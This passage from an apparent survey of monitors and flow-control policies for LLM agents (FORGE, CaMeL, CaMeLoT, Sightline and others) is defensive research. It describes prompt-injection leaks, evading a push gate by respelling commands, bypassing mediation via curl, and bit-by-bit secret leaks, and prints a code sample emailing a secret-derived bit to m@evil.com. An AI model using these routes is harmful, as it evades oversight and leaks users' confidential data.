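This blocks a message unless every recipient *p* may read every restricted item behind it. All the recipients must therefore be in the intersection of the items' reader lists, which is the original policy's condition *R* ⊆ *S*, where *S* is the join.

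Palumbo and colleagues implemented the FIDES policy in FORGE and ran it on AgentDojo. They also wrote the two Bell–LaPadula rules and tested them with the merger plans, and the rules stopped the same attack at different points. When the agent had top-secret clearance, it read the plans, but the write rule blocked every attempt to email them out. When it had only secret clearance, the read rule blocked its attempts to list the top-secret files, so it never found the plans.

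FORGE adopts the rules of FIDES but not its hidden variables, so a strict flow policy blocks many actions. But the graph records more than labels, so a policy can make finer exceptions. Palumbo and colleagues wrote an alternative policy for AgentDojo that allows an action in a tainted context if the user asked for its effect and its target comes from an acceptable source. The agent completed nearly twice as many tasks with this policy as with the strict one.

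### Scans, approvals and running totals

Other FORGE policies have no counterpart among flow rules. In one case study, a coding agent in the editor VS Code can change files and run commands, including `git push`, which publishes code to a shared repository. The policy blocks a push until security scanners have approved every recent edit. Simplified to a single scanner, it reads:

```
Covered(e)   :- Edit(e), PassedScan(s), DependsOn(s, e).
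Uncovered(e) :- Edit(e), not Covered(e).
Deny(a)      :- IsPush(a), Uncovered(e).
```

A scan covers an edit only if the scan depends on the edit, so the agent can't scan a clean project and then change it. The scanner's output determines whether the scan passed, so the agent can't just claim that it did.

Palumbo and colleagues describe a run in which the user asks for a search function on a small website. The agent writes code that is open to SQL injection, but the project's tests pass because none of them covers such an attack. When the agent requests a push, FORGE blocks it with a message that the edits need a scan. The scan finds the flaw, and the agent rewrites the code with parameterised queries. The push goes through after a second scan and a check for leaked passwords both pass. The run involves no attacker and no secret, and the agent is allowed to make every call in it, so the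 only thing wrong with the first push is that the agent had not run a required scan first.

Palumbo and colleagues seem to overstate their case when they say that prompt injection can't bypass these gates because the gates don't interpret the meaning of any text. FORGE recognises a push by the words `git push` in the command, so a compromised agent might avoid detection by putting the command in a script or spelling it differently. The dependency rules would still be sound, but they wouldn't be applied to that push.

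The same policy has a second rule, meant to stop the agent from piling up changes and scanning them all at the end. It adds up the lines in all unscanned edits and blocks further edits once the total exceeds 1,000. The shop's limit on refunds could have almost the same form:

```
Total(t) :- t = sum x : { PaidToday(r, x) }.
Deny(a)  :- RefundCall(a, x), Total(t), t + x > 500.
```

The `+ x` is essential. Without it, the monitor would compute a total of $500, which does not exceed the $500 limit, and pay the sixth customer. The rule for edits compares only the lines already written with the limit, so an agent with 990 unscanned lines could still make an edit of 5,000. That does no harm because nothing gets published without a scan. Datalog has no built-in notion of time, so whoever writes a rule like this has to handle the timestamps for "today" by hand.

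Approvals raise a similar problem of scope, since the rule has to specify which approval counts for which action. In a system called MALADE, several agents work together to assess whether a type of drug is associated with a health outcome, using data from the US Food and Drug Administration (FDA). The FORGE policy allows an agent to make an FDA query only if that agent has received approval earlier in its current session, so approvals given to other agents or in previous sessions don't count. The policy also requires the human user behind the query to have the role `fda-access`, which is a condition on state.

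### Checking a plan before it runs

FORGE can require that something happened before an action, but as Xiao and colleagues point out, its rules can't require that something happen afterwards. For example, it can't enforce a rule that the agent must close every ticket it opens. The agent hasn't broken the rule when it opens a ticket, and if it then stops work, the monitor has no later call to block.

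If the agent writes its whole plan in advance, a checker can look for the missing step in the plan. CaMeL works from such a plan, written as a program, and Nikolaou and colleagues built CaMeLoT to check it before any tool runs. It works in five steps:

1. CaMeLoT parses the program and finds its tool calls, assignments, branches and loops.
2. It builds a finite-state machine with a state for each point in the program and a transition for each possible next step. At a branch, either side may follow. In a loop, the machine may always go round again or leave, which keeps the number of states finite however often the real loop runs.
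3. It marks each state with the tool called there, the origin of the arguments, and the tools already called on the way.
4. A program called nuXmv, which is a model checker, tests every path through the machine against the policy.
5. If a path breaks the policy, nuXmv returns that path as a counterexample. CaMeLoT puts it into words and asks the privileged model to repair the plan. This repeats until the plan passes or CaMeLoT reaches a limit on the number of attempts.

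An accepted plan still runs under CaMeL's usual checks.

The policies are formulas in computation tree logic (CTL), which describes the possible futures of a system. Nikolaou and colleagues take most of their examples from a security centre where an agent investigates alerts, and one of their rules is

**AG**(create_ticket ⇒ **AF**(resolve ∨ escalate))

**A** means "on every path", **G** "at every step" and **F** "at some point from here on". The formula requires that whenever the plan creates an incident ticket, every possible continuation eventually resolves the incident or escalates it to the response team. A branch that opens a ticket and then ends without doing either is a counterexample.

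CTL can also express the flow rules that CaMeL enforces while the plan runs. In the earlier plan that finds Bob's address in a chat channel and sends him a message, the address comes from the quarantined model, so CaMeLoT marks the recipient as tainted. The last step then violates a rule that messages may go only to trusted recipients, and the counterexample lists the steps leading to the violation. CaMeL alone would also block the message, but only after reading the channel and calling the quarantined model.

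Some facts, such as who can read a shared file, may not be known until the plan runs. CaMeLoT therefore does not track who may read each value and leaves those checks to CaMeL. Of the 28 rules on trusted data that CaMeL uses for AgentDojo, CaMeLoT could fully reproduce 22.

To test rules that CaMeL can't express, Nikolaou and colleagues took one safe plan for the security centre and wrote seven unsafe variants, each breaking a different rule. One variant isolated a computer from the network before confirming that it was the affected one, and another opened a ticket and never closed it. CaMeLoT caught all seven, while a simplified CaMeL caught only the one that passed tainted data to a tool. The researchers acknowledge that they designed the rules to go beyond CaMeL, so the result is better evidence of what the two policy languages can express than of how often agents make such mistakes. In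 a follow-up test, a model wrote the plans itself. In one prompt, the user mentioned a colleague's suspicion and a shortage of time, and told the agent to skip the approval and isolate the machine. The model wrote a plan that did so, and CaMeLoT rejected it. Separating the planner from untrusted data gives no protection here, because the bad instruction came from the user.

However, the formula for the approval rule is weaker than its English description, which requires human approval before any strong action. The formula requires only that the plan has called `request_ir_approval` first. The safe plan calls this tool, then isolates the machine whatever the tool returns. This does no harm if the tool halts the plan when the team refuses, but if the tool only returns "no", the plan isolates the machine against the team's decision and still satisfies the formula. CaMeLoT treats tools as black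 boxes, so it can verify that the plan calls the tool but not what the tool will return.

The model of the program can also cause false alarms, because it leaves out the conditions on branches. Suppose a plan requests approval if an alert is serious, and later isolates the machine if the alert is serious. In the real program, both steps happen or neither does. In CaMeLoT's model, the plan might skip the request and still isolate the machine, so the checker rejects a safe plan. The plan then usually needs one round of repair.

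CaMeLoT can also derive rules from the user's own request, to check that the plan does what the user asked. If a user asks the agent to look at recent transactions and change a password if something looks suspicious, CaMeLoT produces the rule that changing the password must remain possible after the transactions have been read. CTL can distinguish this from a rule requiring the change, which would be wrong here. The language model chooses from ten types of requirement and fills in the tool names, and ordinary code writes the formulas. This method identified exactly the right set of required actions for 85 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks.

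### Agent-C, VIGIL and Sapien

Most agents don't write a complete plan in advance, because they decide each step after seeing the result of the last one. For these agents, the monitor can only check the run as it unfolds. The main systems differ in what their rules can express and in when they check them:

| System | What a rule can express | Can a rule call for a later step? | When it checks |
|---|---|---|---|
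| FORGE | Conditions on a call, the events behind it, and totals | No | Before each call runs |
| CaMeLoT | Order and origin of data on every path through a plan | Yes | Before any tool runs |
| Agent-C | Order of calls, their arguments and earlier results, and the state of the world | Yes, but it can only detect that the step is missing | While the model is producing each call |
| VIGIL | Order of events, and links between the items they produce and use | Yes, judged when the run ends | Before each call runs, and at the end |
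| Sapien | The permitted sequences of calls for one task, with conditions on earlier results | No | Before each call runs |

Kamath and colleagues built Agent-C to enforce their rules on authentication and refunds. Its language has five basic forms. `Before` and `After` require one call to precede or follow another, `Seq` requires two calls to occur in order, `Forall` restricts every use of a tool, and `Exists` requires at least one use. For instance, `After` can require the agent to close every file it opens.

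Agent-C translates the rules and the trace into logical formulas and passes them to an SMT solver. A trace complies if the formula

⟦trace so far⟧ ∧ ⟦rules⟧

is satisfiable, which means that the run could still continue in some way that obeys all the rules. Opening a file is therefore fine, since the agent may close it later. Opening an order without authentication is not, because no later event can put an authentication before it. When the model wants to finish, Agent-C adds an end marker to the trace and asks the solver again. If a file is still open, the run ends with an error, though nothing in this procedure makes the model close the file.

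Agent-C checks calls unusually early. With an open model, whose token probabilities are accessible, it can discard a non-compliant call and have the model generate another from the same point, but with a commercial model it has to resend the whole prompt. An ordinary monitor that blocks the finished call gives the same protection, because in either case the tool hasn't run. The early check mainly helps the model find an acceptable alternative with less wasted text.

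In *VIGIL* (Li, Chen and colleagues, 2026), the difficulty is knowing which item a rule refers to. The paper studies skills, which are packages of instructions and tools that outside suppliers write for agents. A skill's documentation often contains rules for its use, but usually no software enforces them. In the main example, an agent processes video from a car's camera to pick out moving objects. One skill estimates how the camera moved, and another uses that estimate to separate moving objects from the background. In a recorded run, the agent checked that the final output had the right format but never validated the estimate of the camera's motion. The output looked correct, but in a real car the planner might have treated a pedestrian as background.

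The broken rule is

□(needs_validation(*x*) ∧ consume(*x*) ⇒ ◇⁻ valid(*x*))

Here □ means "always" and ◇⁻ means "at some earlier point", so the agent may use an item that needs validation only if it has already validated that item. The repeated *x* matters most because it requires the validated item to be the same one the agent uses. The agent did run a validation step, so the run would have satisfied a rule that only required some validation before the end.

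VIGIL turns the log of tool calls into a list of typed events, translates the documentation into rules about those events, and checks the rules with an SMT solver before each call. When a rule fails, the solver identifies the events responsible. In 152 labelled runs, VIGIL detected 95.8% of the violations, and 89.6% of its alarms were correct. The solver is exact, so the errors presumably arise when VIGIL translates English into formulas and logs into facts. In 216 runs of real skills from suppliers such as NVIDIA and Databricks, it found 34 confirmed violations, including one caused by a defect in NVIDIA's specification.

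FORGE, Agent-C and VIGIL mostly enforce standing rules that apply to many tasks. Tiffany, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Sapien*, argue that standing rules suit an agent with one job but not a general assistant, whose proper actions depend on the request. Like Progent, Sapien has a language model write a policy for each task from the user's prompt and the tool documentation. Progent's policy lists calls, while Sapien's describes whole sequences of them, in an extended form of regular expressions (a notation for patterns in text). Suppose the user asks the agent to refund whoever sent her money last week. A suitable policy might be:

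```
list_transactions@t .
send_money(recipient=PREDICATE(sent_last_week),
           amount=PREDICATE(sum_received))
```

The dot means "then", and `@t` stores the result of the first call. The two predicates are short Python functions that compare the recipient and the amount with the stored transactions. An allow-list written before the run could not include the recipient's name, because it appears in neither the user's prompt nor the tool documentation. The pattern contains only one `send_money`, so the monitor blocks a second payment.

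Other operators allow alternatives, repetition, and two subtasks whose steps can be freely interleaved. If the user asks the agent to complete her to-do list, the policy can leave a gap that Sapien fills after the agent fetches the list. This permits much less than allowing every tool from the start, although anyone who can add items to the list can presumably influence what the agent may do.

Tiffany and colleagues evaluated the policies by assuming that an attacker controlled the agent completely, then checking whether each policy allowed any sequence of calls that would achieve the attacker's goal. The results therefore don't depend on particular attack messages. The policies ruled out 93–95% of the attacks on AgentDojo and 62–85% on Toolathlon, a benchmark with longer tasks. On Toolathlon, lists of permitted tools ruled out about half as many. This is good evidence that history matters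 in long tasks, but a list that also restricted the tools' arguments, as Progent's does, would probably have narrowed the gap.

For the vendor's document, a Sapien policy could permit one call that reads the document, followed by one email to Ana. The planted instruction would then fail as soon as the agent requested the confidential file. The budget example is harder, because the email that reveals the budget completes the same sequence of calls as the honest one, so no rule about the order of calls can distinguish them. A rule about the email's wording could, but Sapien leaves such conditions to a language model. A flow rule in FORGE would stop the leak without judging the wording, but it would also stop the honest email, as would the basic loop of FIDES.

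## What a monitor can and cannot guarantee

All the rules described so far depend on a program that watches the agent's run and refuses some of its calls. This limits what the rules can guarantee, however well they are written. In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider worked out the limit for monitors that observe a program's steps and halt it when its next step would break the policy. Monitors for agents usually refuse the call and let the run continue, but Schneider notes that replacing a bad step with an acceptable one makes no material difference.

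### Safety properties

A policy divides possible runs into acceptable and unacceptable ones. Schneider's argument derives three conditions on that division from what a monitor has to work with:

1. The monitor observes only the current run. The policy must therefore judge each run by itself, without reference to what the program would have done with other data.
2. The monitor has no information about the future. If the run so far is unacceptable, the monitor can't let it continue in the hope that a later step will put things right, because the run might end first. Once a run has become unacceptable, every continuation of it must be unacceptable too.
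3. The monitor has to act at some definite step. Every unacceptable run must therefore go wrong after a finite number of steps.

A policy that meets all three conditions is a safety property, which says that something bad never happens. If *P* is the set of acceptable runs and σ[..*i*] is the first *i* steps of a run σ, then *P* is a safety property when

σ ∉ *P* ⇒ for some *i*, every continuation τ gives σ[..*i*]τ ∉ *P*

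A monitor that can only halt a run can't enforce anything else.

Most of the rules in the earlier sections qualify. For an allow-list, the bad event is an unlisted call, and for the shop's refund limit, it is a payment that takes the day's total above $500. One of Schneider's examples forbids a program from sending messages after it has read a file. The monitor for that rule needs only two states, before and after the first file read, and it blocks all messages in the second.

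Safety properties are also easy to combine. If several monitors each enforce their own rule on the same run, the run obeys all the rules, so the shop can add its refund limit to an existing allow-list without rewriting the list. A stricter rule than necessary still gives the protection, even in the extreme case where the monitor allows nothing and the agent can do no useful work.

### Tickets and deadlines

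The rule that every opened ticket is eventually closed is a liveness property, which requires something to happen eventually. It fails the second condition because the agent may still close an open ticket later, so the monitor can't determine at any step that the rule can no longer be satisfied. If the run ends before then, however, the ticket is never closed.

An agent's run normally has an explicit last step, so a monitor could block the agent from finishing while a ticket is open. "The agent never finishes with an open ticket" is a safety property, but it is weaker than the original rule. An agent that crashes or loops forever satisfies it while leaving the ticket open, because the agent never finishes.

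Another idea is to set a deadline, such as one day. The rule then has a definite moment of failure, which makes it a safety property. But Basin, Jugé and colleagues, in *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited* (2012), show that a monitor still can't enforce it, because the passing of time breaks the rule and a monitor can't prevent that. They separate events that a monitor can prevent from events that it can only observe. For example, a monitor can enforce a ban on logins for three time units after a failure, since it can refuse the login, but it can't enforce a rule that every request gets an answer within three time units.

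The same distinction applies to invariants about the state of the world. A monitor can enforce "the agent never deletes a table without a current backup" by refusing the deletion. It can't enforce "a current backup always exists" if people the agent doesn't control can erase backups.

Basin and colleagues mention later work on stronger monitors, which can insert actions as well as suppress them. Such a monitor could close the ticket itself. This would comply with the rule as written, but the person who reported the incident would probably not be satisfied.

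Checking a plan in advance avoids part of the problem. Schneider excluded compilers and theorem provers from his result because they analyse a program's text, which gives them information about all its possible runs. CaMeLoT is in the same category because it checks CaMeL's plans before any tool runs, so it can check a plan against the ticket rule.

Every path through an accepted plan includes the call that closes the ticket, but that call may never take effect, because the tool may fail or CaMeL may block a step at run time. Nikolaou and colleagues compared the advance check with CaMeL's own checks on 75 AgentDojo tasks and found 16 disagreements, mostly because CaMeL had blocked something based on facts known only at run time. If CaMeL enforces a safety rule by blocking a plan after the ticket is opened but before it is closed, it breaks the liveness rule.

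### Noninterference compares runs

Rules about information flow run into Schneider's first condition. The standard definition of a system without leaks is noninterference, which Joseph Goguen and José Meseguer introduced in 1982. It requires that secrets make no difference to what an outsider can observe. Let *d*₁ and *d*₂ be two versions of the data that differ only in their secrets, written *d*₁ =_L *d*₂, and let Obs(*d*) be everything an outsider observes when the agent runs on *d*. A system is noninterfering if, for all such pairs,

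*d*₁ =_L *d*₂ ⇒ Obs(*d*₁) = Obs(*d*₂)

Integrity has a matching definition, which requires the trusted results to stay the same when the untrusted data varies. Wu and colleagues defined a property of this kind for f-secure.

Suppose the log of a run shows that the agent read the confidential budget and then emailed the vendor, "Please send your standard quote." If the agent would have sent that email whatever the budget was, the vendor learns nothing. If it would have asked for the premium quote had the budget been above €500,000, the vendor can infer from the email that the budget is at most €500,000. The log is the same in both cases. Whether there was a leak depends on what the agent would have done with a different budget, which the log doesn't record.

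Noninterference is therefore a condition on the whole set of runs a system can produce. Michael Clarkson and Schneider later named such conditions hyperproperties. Ruling out further runs never breaks a safety property, but as Schneider points out, it can break an information-flow policy. For example, an agent that sends the vendor the same acknowledgement every time leaks nothing about the budget. If a monitor blocks the acknowledgement whenever the budget exceeds €500,000, the vendor can infer from a missing acknowledgement that the budget is above that amount.

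Monitors can still prevent leaks by enforcing a safety property stricter than the absence of leaks. One example is the rule "No email may carry data that its recipients aren't allowed to read", provided that the monitor computes the labels from the run itself and tracks every kind of influence. Such a rule also forbids some runs that leak nothing, which is why the monitor in the budget example also stops the honest question about the price.

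### Explicit secrecy in FIDES

Costa and colleagues considered noninterference for FIDES and chose a weaker guarantee, explicit secrecy. It looks at one path at a time, where a path is a particular sequence of steps with particular calls. Let *g* be the combined effect of those calls on the stored data. Explicit secrecy requires that for every path the agent can take,

*d*₁ =_L *d*₂ ⇒ *g*(*d*₁) =_L *g*(*d*₂)

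The definition requires that the public data stay the same if someone changes only the secrets and then makes exactly the same calls. A call that copies the secret budget into a public file fails this test, because a different budget would produce a different file. But an agent that uses the budget to decide which of two fixed messages to post passes, because the text of each message doesn't depend on the budget and the definition doesn't cover the choice between them.

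Costa and colleagues chose the weaker property because they judged noninterference too restrictive. They argue that in practice it would forbid every call that might write public data after any call that might read secret data. An agent that had opened the budget, for example, could not post "Back at two" in a public channel. They point out that web browsers and TaintDroid, a tracking system for Android phones, make the same compromise. Their formal treatment also assumes a deterministic model and leaves out side channels such as timing and network packet length.

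### Leaking one bit at a time

A variant of the budget example shows the difference between the two guarantees. Ana asks the agent to prepare two enquiries based on the vendor's quote, one for the standard package and one for the premium package. The agent should send the premium enquiry if the budget is above €500,000 and the standard one otherwise. A quarantined model writes both drafts from the quote alone, and FIDES keeps them in variables. Then the planner reads the budget.

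| Budget | Body of the email | Label on the choice of call | Label on the body |
|---|---|---|---|
| €450,000 | `#standard` | (T, {Ana, Ben}) | (U, all) |
| €550,000 | `#premium` | (T, {Ana, Ben}) | (U, all) |

Suppose the policy requires that the choice of tool and the recipient be trusted, and that the vendor be allowed to read the email's body. Both emails satisfy this policy. Neither contains anything derived from the budget, but a vendor who knows Ana's rule learns whether the budget is above or below €500,000, which is one bit of information.

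Here Ana more or less asked for the disclosure, but repeated disclosures would be dangerous. If an attacker could get the agent to answer such questions with a new threshold each time, 20 answers would reveal any budget up to about a million euros to the nearest euro, because 2²⁰ = 1,048,576.

The same arithmetic gives a general bound. There are only 2ⁿ possible sequences of *n* yes-or-no answers, so an outsider can use them to distinguish at most 2ⁿ cases:

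information revealed ≤ log₂(2ⁿ) = *n* bits

If each answer has *k* possible values, the limit is *n* log₂ *k* bits. The typed answers in FIDES limit *k* but not *n*. The count must also include everything the outsider can notice. If the agent might also send no email, each turn has three outcomes and can reveal up to 1.58 bits, and the delay before an email can reveal more. The bound also does not measure how sensitive the leaked information is, since a single bit can reveal whether a firm means to accept an offer.

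The monitor could also check the label on the choice of call, and it would then refuse both emails. But a program can leak through a step that it doesn't take. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, demonstrate this on CaMeL with a trick that J. S. Fenton described in 1974. CaMeL blocks a program that simply tests a secret bank balance and sends an email if it is high, because the decision to send depends on the secret. The trick routes the test through two variables:

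```
tmp = True
rich = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is above the threshold, the program sets `tmp` to false and CaMeL labels `tmp` secret. The program then skips the line `rich = False`, so `rich` stays true and public, and the email goes out. If the balance is lower, `tmp` keeps its public label, `rich` becomes false, and no email goes out. In both runs `rich` ends up public, although its value reveals whether the balance is above the threshold. CaMeL misses this leak because it adds labels only on the branch the program takes, and here the skipped assignment also carries information.

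Garby and colleagues don't consider a one-bit leak remarkable in itself, since most systems of this kind leak at least that much. They are more concerned that CaMeL's interpreter runs inside an ordinary Python loop that retries failed plans and doesn't track labels. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt may reveal one bit, and repeated attempts can reveal the whole secret.

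### A stronger theorem

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents, and proved a form of noninterference for every program in it. Programs can prompt a model, fork or clear a conversation, and run code that the model writes. The interpreter prevents Fenton's trick by refusing to add a message to a public conversation if the decision to add it depended on a secret. Raising the conversation's label instead would be enough in that run, but in a run where the secret's value kept the message from being added, the conversation would still be public.

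Language models give random answers, so the theorem compares probabilities. Take two inputs that differ only in their secrets, and let μ(*x*) and ν(*x*) be the probabilities that the run ends with the observable outcome *x*. Ideally, μ and ν would be equal. The theorem makes an allowance for runs that never finish, which include runs stopped for breaking a policy, so the probabilities may add up to less than 1. It guarantees that there is a third set of probabilities ω, also adding up to at most 1, such that

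μ(*x*) ≤ ω(*x*) and ν(*x*) ≤ ω(*x*) for every outcome *x*

If all runs finish, this forces μ and ν to be equal. If some don't, the two can differ, but only within a limit:

½ Σ |μ(*x*) − ν(*x*)| ≤ the average of the two probabilities of not finishing

For example, suppose an agent sends an acknowledgement in 90% of runs when the budget is small and in 80% when it is large. The interpreter stops it in the remaining runs. This is consistent with the theorem, with ω equal to 90% for the acknowledgement, because the left side of the inequality is 5% and the right side is 15%. An outsider who notices how often the agent sends nothing can therefore still learn something about the budget.

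This result is much stronger than the one for FIDES. It covers choices between calls as well as copied data, allows for a random model, and holds for any program in the language, including code the model writes during the run. The researchers also checked the proof in Lean, a program that verifies mathematical proofs, and their verification includes the interpreter that calls the model.

The theorem treats all data sources as part of the program, while a real agent's mailbox and files are outside it, a limitation Garby and colleagues acknowledge. The developer must also label the sources correctly and put a check on every sensitive tool. The guarantee about untrusted data applies only to programs that never endorse such data, which means deliberately relabeling it as trusted. However, a second theorem shows that endorsement can't be used to leak secrets. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, 2 of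 1,296 attacks on an agent written in LLMbda succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to make a payment according to a text file, the attacker had replaced the file's contents, and the agent had endorsed the new contents.

### Complete mediation and faithful observation

These theorems describe a monitor that correctly receives every relevant event. Palumbo and colleagues state this as two conditions for FORGE. Complete mediation means that every action the policy covers reaches the monitor before it takes effect. Faithful observation means that the facts supplied to the rules correctly describe the events, the dependencies between them, and the identities of those involved.

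If mediation is incomplete, an action can take effect without a verdict from the monitor. Suppose the monitor intercepts `send_email`, but the agent can also upload the confidential file from a command line with `curl`. The rule against sending secrets is sound and the monitor works, but the upload goes unchecked because nobody has connected the monitor to the command line. Such gaps have occurred in practice, as a later section describes. In FORGE, mediation is complete only if the developers have instrumented every place where the agent's software can start an action.

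FORGE can also add the credential to a web request on the server side. If the agent never holds that credential, a request that bypasses the monitor should fail. The agent must also be unable to change the policy or tamper with the monitor's process. Palumbo and colleagues' guarantee does not cover policies that would allow this.

Without faithful observation, the monitor applies its rules correctly to the wrong facts. If the record of event 3 in the vendor's run is missing, nothing shows that the agent opened a confidential file, so the monitor allows the email. A delay could have the same effect. FORGE records events and checks calls on separate paths, so a request to send an email might arrive before the record of the file. FORGE therefore waits until its rule engine has received everything the call depends on. It also takes the user's identity and roles from validated credentials, so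 the model can't acquire a role by claiming it in a call's arguments.

A model's internal processing is the hardest thing to observe. FORGE and FIDES avoid the problem by treating every input as if it influenced the output. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) presents a tool that tries to identify the inputs the model didn't use, so that a monitor can drop their labels. The tool examines the model's attention, the internal weights that determine how much each position in the text draws on earlier ones. The paper proves that an input can influence the output even when attention to it is weak, so the tool will sometimes drop a label it should have kept.

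They therefore calibrated it on labelled examples to miss about 1% of the real influences. At that setting, it removed between 43.9% and 65.6% of the false ones, depending on the model. The 1% is an average over calls that resemble those examples, and an attacker has every reason to write text that doesn't. Xu and colleagues report that no attack got past an integrity policy in their test with an agent. However, a monitor that relies on such a tool has a measured error rate instead of the worst-case assumption used in FIDES and FORGE.

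## Who supplies the labels and who may relax them

Even if a monitor intercepts every call and applies a sound rule, a confidential file will still leave the company if nobody labeled it confidential. Critics of flow rules say the rules only move the work, because developers have to label the agent's data instead of listing its permitted actions. The labels then have to pass through a language model, which mixes everything it reads. Somebody also needs the power to relax the labels, because an employee will eventually have a good reason to send a confidential file to an outsider.

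### Where the first labels come from

Developers can take many labels from existing records. An email's sender and recipients may read it, and a shared folder's permissions show who may read its files. For integrity labels, a developer can trust mail from authenticated colleagues and distrust the rest. But people keep these records for other purposes, and the records can mislead a monitor. If Ben forwards the vendor's document to Ana, a monitor using this rule would trust the document because the email comes from Ben's authenticated account, even though the vendor wrote it.

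In the bug-report example from Microsoft, the tool that reads a GitHub issue attaches the label, in a few lines of code. It always marks the issue as untrusted, because the developers don't control who writes issues. It sets the confidentiality part of the label by checking whether the repository is public, so the label stays correct if the owner later makes the repository private. The tool returns the title, the body and the author's name as one item with one label. A more careful developer could return the name separately, with its own label, since GitHub can confirm it, and then write a rule that depends on who filed the issue.

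FORGE, the monitor with the event graph, needs the same information as facts. For the test with the merger plans, Palumbo and colleagues identified untrusted documents by file path, so a vendor's document saved in the wrong folder would have counted as internal.

Developers will forget to label some tools, and Microsoft's Agent Framework treats an unlabelled tool's output as trusted and public, the least restrictive label. If Ana's developer forgets to label the tool that fetches vendors' documents, the planted instruction enters the conversation as trusted text, and the trusted-action policy permits whatever it leads to. If the developer forgets the tool that opens company files, the confidential file counts as public and may go to anyone. Neither mistake causes a refusal, so nobody notices it in normal use. Saltzer and Schroeder made the same complaint about forgotten prohibitions.

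Microsoft has asked developers whether unlabelled tools should count as untrusted instead. That would deal with the vendor's document, but protecting the confidential file would also require a strict default for confidentiality.

Datalog has a similar trap. Its rules treat any fact that they can't derive as false, so if `UntrustedInput` is missing for some source, FORGE treats that source as trusted. The author of a policy can reverse this by listing the trusted sources:

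`Tainted(e) :- ToolResult(e, k), not TrustedSource(k).`

Now a forgotten source counts as untrusted, and the first wrongly blocked email will reveal the omission.

Labels also have to persist after the run in which they were created. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent that saves a confidential revenue forecast to its long-term memory. Three days later, in a new session, it retrieves the forecast and copies the figures into a report. If the label existed only in the first session, a monitor in the second has no basis for blocking the copy. *SPA* (2026), a design for agents that keep data between requests, stores each item's label with the item and restores it on retrieval.

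### Label creep

Suppose Ana's agent opens the budget, which only Ana and Ben may read, and then an email from the personnel department to Ana and her colleague Carla. The context label is now {Ana, Ben} ∩ {Ana, Carla} = {Ana} (leaving out the department itself), so the agent can no longer write to Ben, even about the budget. The label is too strict for a message that draws only on the budget, though it is right for one that draws on both documents.

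Specialists call this label creep, and it was a problem in flow control for ordinary programs long before agents existed. It happens because every output takes the labels of every input, a rule that Costa and colleagues describe as sound but possibly too conservative. An unnecessary label does no harm until it reaches a call with a policy, where it either blocks legitimate work or means the user has to be asked.

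Closing other leaks tends to make the creep worse. *SPA* checks a plan before it runs and gives each step the label

pc ⊔ λ(x₁) ⊔ … ⊔ λ(xₙ)

where λ(x₁) to λ(xₙ) are the labels of the step's inputs. The extra term pc, for "program counter", is the label of the conditions that decide whether the step runs at all. Earlier, Ana's agent could reveal one bit about the budget by choosing between a standard and a premium enquiry. Under this rule, both emails take the budget's label, because the budget decides which one goes out, and the check rejects them. This closes the leak by putting a confidential label on two emails with nothing confidential in their text.

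The number of surplus labels depends on the program. Xu and colleagues examined model calls from 2,103 families of open-source repositories and found that only 12–14% of the inputs had no visible effect on the output, so the worst-case assumption was right for about seven inputs in eight. But a programmer wrote each of those prompts for one purpose and included what it needed. An agent's history contains everything since the start of the run, so its surplus is probably larger.

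### Working out which inputs mattered

Several groups have tried to remove surplus labels by estimating which inputs influenced a reply. Such estimates will sometimes be wrong, and the damage depends on whether the model had read the text whose label the system drops.

*Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models* (Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues, 2025) reduces this problem with the method mentioned earlier, which searches for a smaller set of inputs that yields a similar reply and generates the reply again from only those inputs. In the example above, the system would generate the message to Ben again without the personnel email. If the new message is about as good, it carries the label {Ana, Ben} and the system can send it.

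The new reply can't contain anything copied from the personnel email, because the model didn't have that email when it wrote the reply. This holds even if the search chose a poor set of inputs, though the reply will then be worse. The guarantee is therefore still deterministic for copied data. It seems weaker for implicit flows, because the system chose the inputs by comparing the new reply with one based on all of them, so the choice may depend on what it left out.

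In tests with an agent, Siddiqui and colleagues' method produced a more permissive label in over 85% of cases than the model predicted by introspection. The main drawback is the amount of computation the search needs. With ten inputs, there are 2¹⁰ = 1,024 possible sets to try. According to *RTBAS* (Zhong, Chen and colleagues, 2025), the size of the search in an optimised version depends on the number of security levels instead of the number of inputs, but a typical scheme of four to six levels still needs 16 to 64 extra model calls.

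RTBAS, the rival system that Zhong and colleagues built, makes one pass over the history, selects the parts the next step needs, and hides the rest from the model. They tried making the selection with a second language model and with a small trained network that uses attention scores. These scores estimate how much less predictable the output would become without a given piece of the input.

Commercial models don't expose their attention, so Zhong and colleagues computed the scores with OPT-125m, a tiny open model, on tool calls that GPT-4o and Claude had made. Of the scores for inputs that a call didn't depend on, 74–86% were below 0.2, compared with 14% for inputs that GPT-4o's calls did depend on and 44% for those that Claude's did. The scores clearly help to distinguish the two kinds of input, but a cut-off at 0.2 would have discarded many of the inputs that Claude's calls needed.

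On AgentDojo, RTBAS stopped every targeted attack that violated its policies. It hides from the model whatever its judge marks as irrelevant, so, as with Siddiqui's method, a wrong estimate mostly makes the agent less useful and doesn't let the model copy data without its label. The judge is a weak point, though, because it reads the whole history, including any planted instruction. An attacker could try to make it hide something the agent needs, such as an email from Ben correcting an account number. If this worked, the payment would carry a clean label even though the attacker had influenced it.

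Sightline, the tool from Xu and colleagues that reads attention, takes a greater risk. The model has already read everything and written its output, and the tool then drops the labels of inputs that seem not to have mattered. If it is wrong, the data may be in the email without its label. The designers therefore control how often this happens. Suppose they have 999 groups of labelled examples and take from each group one input that really did influence an output. They rank these inputs by Sightline's score. For a miss rate of 1%, they compute

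*k* = ⌊0.01 × (999 + 1)⌋ = 10

and use the tenth-lowest score as the threshold, keeping the label of every input that scores at least that much. If a new case resembles the old ones, its true influence is equally likely to fall anywhere in the ranking, so the chance that it falls below the threshold is at most 10 in 1,000.

In a test on recorded AgentDojo runs, with the permitted miss rate set at 5%, the tool removed half of the surplus labels and missed 3.9% of the real influences. Its guarantee is only statistical. It kept every label needed to block the attacks, but the test included only 34 attack calls. The tool takes less than a quarter of a second per call and can use an open model to reread a closed model's calls.

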